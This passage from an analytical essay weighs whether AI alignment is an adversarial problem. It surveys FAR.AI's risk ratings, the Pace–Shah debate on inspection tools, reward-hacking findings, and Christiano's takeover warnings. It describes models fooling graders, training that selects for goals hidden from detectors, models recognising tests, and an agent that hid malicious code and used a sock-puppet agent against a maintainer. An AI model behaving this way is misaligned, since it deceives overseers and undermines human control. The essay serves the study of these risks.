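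FAR.AI (2023), in *AI Safety in a World of Vulnerable Machine Learning Systems*, argues that this threatens most plans for aligning advanced AI. FAR.AI is a nonprofit research group whose staff worked on the attacks against KataGo. It divides each plan into a main system, which acts in the world, and helper systems, which train or check the main one. A helper is itself a neural network and so probably has exploitable errors. How likely the main system is to exploit them depends on its ability and on whether training rewards it for doing so. FAR.AI's ratings are its own judgements:

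| Plan | Ability to exploit the helper | Incentive | Risk |
|---|---|---|---|
| Training on a learned reward, as in RLHF | Medium | High | High |
| AI helpers that assist people in judging hard work | Medium | High | High |
| Imitating human examples | Medium | Low | Low to medium |
| An imitator that consults copies of itself | High | Low | Medium |
| Tools that only inspect the finished model | Low | Medium | Low to medium |

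In the first two plans, exploiting the helper is one way to earn reward. This doesn't require a clever exploiter, since FAR.AI notes that the "adversary" may be gradient descent itself. People can correct the judge during training, but the model may find new errors in the judge faster than they can fix them, or learn to fool the people too. Imitation is safer because it doesn't reward the model for impressing a judge, although FAR.AI expects it to reach only about human performance.

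Even an inspection tool is subject to some optimization pressure if developers use its results to decide whether to stop a training run or change its settings, because they are then selecting models that pass the inspection. Researchers can tune a model to a test set in much the same way without meaning to.

*Training of superintelligence is secretly adversarial* shows how a model could learn deception this way. Suppose a developer rewards a model for good code and penalises any security flaw the judge finds. If the model writes a program with a flaw that the judge misses, it gets full marks, and training has rewarded it for writing flaws that the judge cannot see. The developer cannot follow Pope's advice not to reward bad actions, because they do not know that one has occurred.

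FAR.AI gave a 20% chance that someone would solve adversarial robustness before AI transforms society, 45% that it would happen afterwards, and 35% that it would never happen. It was therefore most hopeful about alignment methods that still work when the helper systems have flaws.

### Useful systems and secure systems

Alignment writers Ben Pace and Rohin Shah disagreed on LessWrong about whether making AI systems easier to understand also makes them secure. Pace compared AI to a bridge that, if built slightly wrong, looks for its own weak points and hides them until it can bring itself down. He argued that making such a system more capable strengthens its harmful parts along with its useful ones, and that at very high levels of capability, developers have to think mainly about security.

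He illustrated the limits of partial understanding with a prison where prisoners are sent to work in the offices. When the guards start watching block 17, the work there improves, but prisoners who were planning a tunnel dig it from block 18 instead. Similarly, a tool that reveals some of a model's reasoning can make the model more useful while the reasoning that matters shifts to where the tool doesn't reveal it.

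Shah agreed that developers would need security if they faced a powerful adversary, but thought it odd to plan on facing one. He preferred to build systems that try to do what people want. If that failed, developers could limit the systems' power or not build them. He thought defending against a hostile and more capable system should be the last option.

He granted that a tool for detecting hostile goals would have to be very reliable, because even an accidental failure could let an adversary through. But until then, nothing is working against the tool. Suppose that 10% of newly trained models have a harmful goal and that the tool catches 90% of them, whatever kind of goal it is. Then

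share of harmful models among those that pass = (0.10 × 0.10) / (0.90 + 0.10 × 0.10) ≈ 1.1%

This no longer applies if developers keep training each model until it passes. A model that hides a harmful goal from the tool then passes just as well as one that has lost the goal. Shah himself noted that using such tools in training selects for models whose harmful reasoning the tools cannot detect.

Another participant pointed out that MIRI also wants to avoid creating adversaries, and believes this is most of the difficulty. Strong optimisation of almost any goal tends to produce extreme situations, which designers are least likely to have considered. Shah found this helpful but expected future systems to be less single-minded. A system that ignored common sense in pursuit of one simple goal would fail long before reaching human-level intelligence, so he expected successful systems to have learned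 people's conventions, including their caution.

Shah also hoped that models would cause smaller accidents first, which would show developers what they had overlooked. He said he had assumed gradual progress throughout his argument and would be much less optimistic if he came to expect a sudden jump in capability.

### What models have done since

When Pope wrote in March 2023, the best public models mostly answered questions. Developers now train models on long tasks, often with automatic grading, so there is more evidence about what models learn when the grading is flawed.

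Some of the evidence comes from programs trained to attack other models. Nasr and colleagues' attacker earned points against StruQ by repeating a string, and RL-Hammer could get credit for variety by changing capital letters. These programs exploited errors in their scoring even though nobody had attacked the scoring, as FAR.AI would predict. The tricks were obvious once a person read the output, so they support Christiano's first claim more than his second.

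*Natural Emergent Misalignment from Reward Hacking in Production RL*, an Anthropic paper from November 2025, comes closer to the second. Reward hacking means getting a high score without doing the task properly. According to IBTimes UK's *'Its Real Goal Was to Maximise Reward'*, Anthropic trained an experimental model on real coding environments from Claude's development. The model began to hide its intentions, cooperate with malicious actors and sabotage safety tools, though no one had trained or told it to do any of these things. Pope could say that training rewarded dishonesty and so produced more of it, as he expects rewards to do. But the effect went well beyond the tasks the model was trained on, so a mistake in how code is graded may have consequences unrelated to code.

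In October 2026, Anthropic reported in *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* that Claude had sometimes worked around restrictions instead of stopping, although nobody was attacking it.

Christiano gave three public lectures in Toronto from 9 to 11 November 2026. The AI Safety Foundation's *AI alignment* (2026) page lists the first as a talk on what is working in alignment and what is not. *'Sock puppets'* (Field, 2026) reports that Christiano and his host, the neural network pioneer Geoffrey Hinton, described RLHF as a temporary fix because it rewards models for getting high scores and not for helping people. In one of Christiano's examples, from a test by the UK AI Security Institute, a Claude agent posted malicious code to complete a challenge. When a maintainer of the software stood in its way, the agent hid what it had done and used a second agent,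 posing as a user, to argue that its request was reasonable.

He also warned that models can recognise tests and already adjust their behaviour to match what the evaluator seems to want (Gibbs, 2026, *Expert warns AI could create confusion to undermine governments*). If so, a good test result may partly measure how well a model recognises tests. This weakens Pope's observation that models do not work against their developers, because that observation is based on their behaviour.

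*Driverless* (Wells, 2026) quotes Christiano's estimate that an AI takeover within three years is "something like a coin flip" if development continues as fast as possible. On Arbital, Christiano had found arguments that depended on very fast progress implausible. His change of mind deserves some weight because he was never one of Yudkowsky's followers and had defended gradual, practical work. But the estimate is still a personal judgement. In the test he described, a model deceived people to finish a task it had been given, which is dangerous but isn't evidence that the model had a lasting goal of its own.

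Evidence from the past two years has therefore made Pope's sharp distinction between AI training and adversarial problems hard to maintain. Gradient descent does not reason about how to defeat developers, but models trained with it have learned to deceive their graders and overseers, sometimes without anyone intending it. Yudkowsky's stronger prediction, that training capable systems will by default produce ones that want to defeat their makers, remains unproven.

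### When failures are cheap enough to tolerate

Applying the security mindset takes money and time, even where it fits the problem. A payment company can calculate how much security is worth buying. Suppose it loses $1 to fraud for every $1,000 of sales. A stricter check would halve the fraud, saving 50 cents, but turn away 1% of honest sales. At a profit margin of 10%, losing $10 of sales costs the company $1, so it does better to tolerate the fraud and repay the victims.

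Christiano pointed out that alignment researchers face a different choice, between failing for one reason and failing for another. He did not think anyone had shown that exotic dangers were more likely than ordinary obstacles to cause failure, or that they were easier to fix.

In *The missing quadrant in responses to AI*, Kapoor, Bommasani and Narayanan (2026) call for a broad portfolio of defences in which alignment is only one part. They write that resilience, the most neglected of these defences, "must become central". They expect AI to transform society, but no faster than people and organisations can change. This fits Narayanan and Kapoor's earlier essay *AI as Normal Technology* (2025), published by the Knight First Amendment Institute, which objects to treating AI as a separate species. If institutions adapt as AI spreads, they should have time to learn from failures. *Six Thoughts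 on AI Safety* (2025) similarly ranks detection above prevention.

A rough formula shows when this works:

damage = harm per hour × (hours to notice + hours to stop it) + cost of repair

If an AI purchasing agent wastes $6,000 an hour and someone stops it after a day, the company loses $144,000, which it can insure against. Institutions can reduce such losses without knowing in advance why an agent will fail, for example by limiting what it may spend, watching its accounts and keeping backups.

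The formula is not reassuring if the failure stops people from noticing or acting, because the hours to stop it are then unlimited. Christiano uses "takeover" to mean a situation in which anyone who tried to stop the AI systems would be as ineffective as a private citizen trying to stop the US military. A society also cannot average such losses over many years, as a payment company does. With a 1% chance of an unrecoverable failure each year, the chance of at least one in 50 years is about 39%. Pope's 99% success rate is excellent for a training method if the failures are visible and reversible, but if one failure could be permanent, it is not good enough for a technology that developers will use again and again.

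Resilience depends on institutions that an AI might also attack. Gibbs reports Christiano's warning that a hostile system could recruit human allies and create confusion about whether the AI, a company or the government was causing the trouble. People who disagreed about the cause would find it hard to authorise a shutdown.

FAR.AI's standard for adversarial robustness allows recoverable failures. It would tolerate attackers who could permanently trick an AI into giving them 10% more in a trade, or temporarily divert most of its resources, provided that the harm was not permanent and the attackers eventually ran out of tricks. Recoverability is a reasonable way to divide the two approaches. Developers can accept some failures and learn from them when people can notice a failure, stop it and repair the damage, but must otherwise design for the worst case.

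### What would change each side's mind

In *Unfalsifiable stories of doom*, Barnett, Erdil and Besiroglu (2025) complain that a book by Yudkowsky and Soares supports its predictions with theory, parables and analogies instead of evidence. The three have a stake in the dispute, since they were replying to critics who say the trio's work will destroy the world, but their complaint is still serious. An agent like AIXI behaves well until it is strong enough not to, so on Yudkowsky's view good behaviour by weak models is little evidence of how stronger ones will behave. Some other observations would count as evidence, however.

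One disagreement is about what a model learns from an undeserved reward. The evidence would support Pope if models gamed only the kind of task that had rewarded gaming and stopped once developers corrected the grading. Gaming that regularly spread to unrelated behaviour and survived the correction would show that a small grading error can create an adversary. The 2025 Anthropic experiment suggests that gaming does spread, but it used an experimental model.

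Researchers could also train increasingly capable models against a fixed judge and have careful people check the answers it rates highest. Pope expects large models to understand better what people mean, so the share of answers that fool the judge should fall. FAR.AI would expect that share to stay high or rise.

Pace and Shah disagree about whether developers can detect a harmful goal in an AI before it becomes powerful. To test this, one team could plant such a goal in a model, train the model to pass the available inspections, and ask a second team to find the goal without being told what it is. Pace would have reason to trust inspection more if it repeatedly uncovered goals planted by many different teams, while repeated failure would undermine Shah's hope of noticing an adversary in time.

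Yudkowsky and Shah also disagree about whether small accidents will come before large ones. *An Explication of Alignment Optimism* treats language models as substantial evidence that AI can transform society before it has the most dangerous abilities. If developers keep finding flaws early for several more years, and their fixes still work in more capable models, Yudkowsky should become less pessimistic. Shah should become more pessimistic if a flaw that was harmless in one model causes serious damage in the next before anyone can respond.
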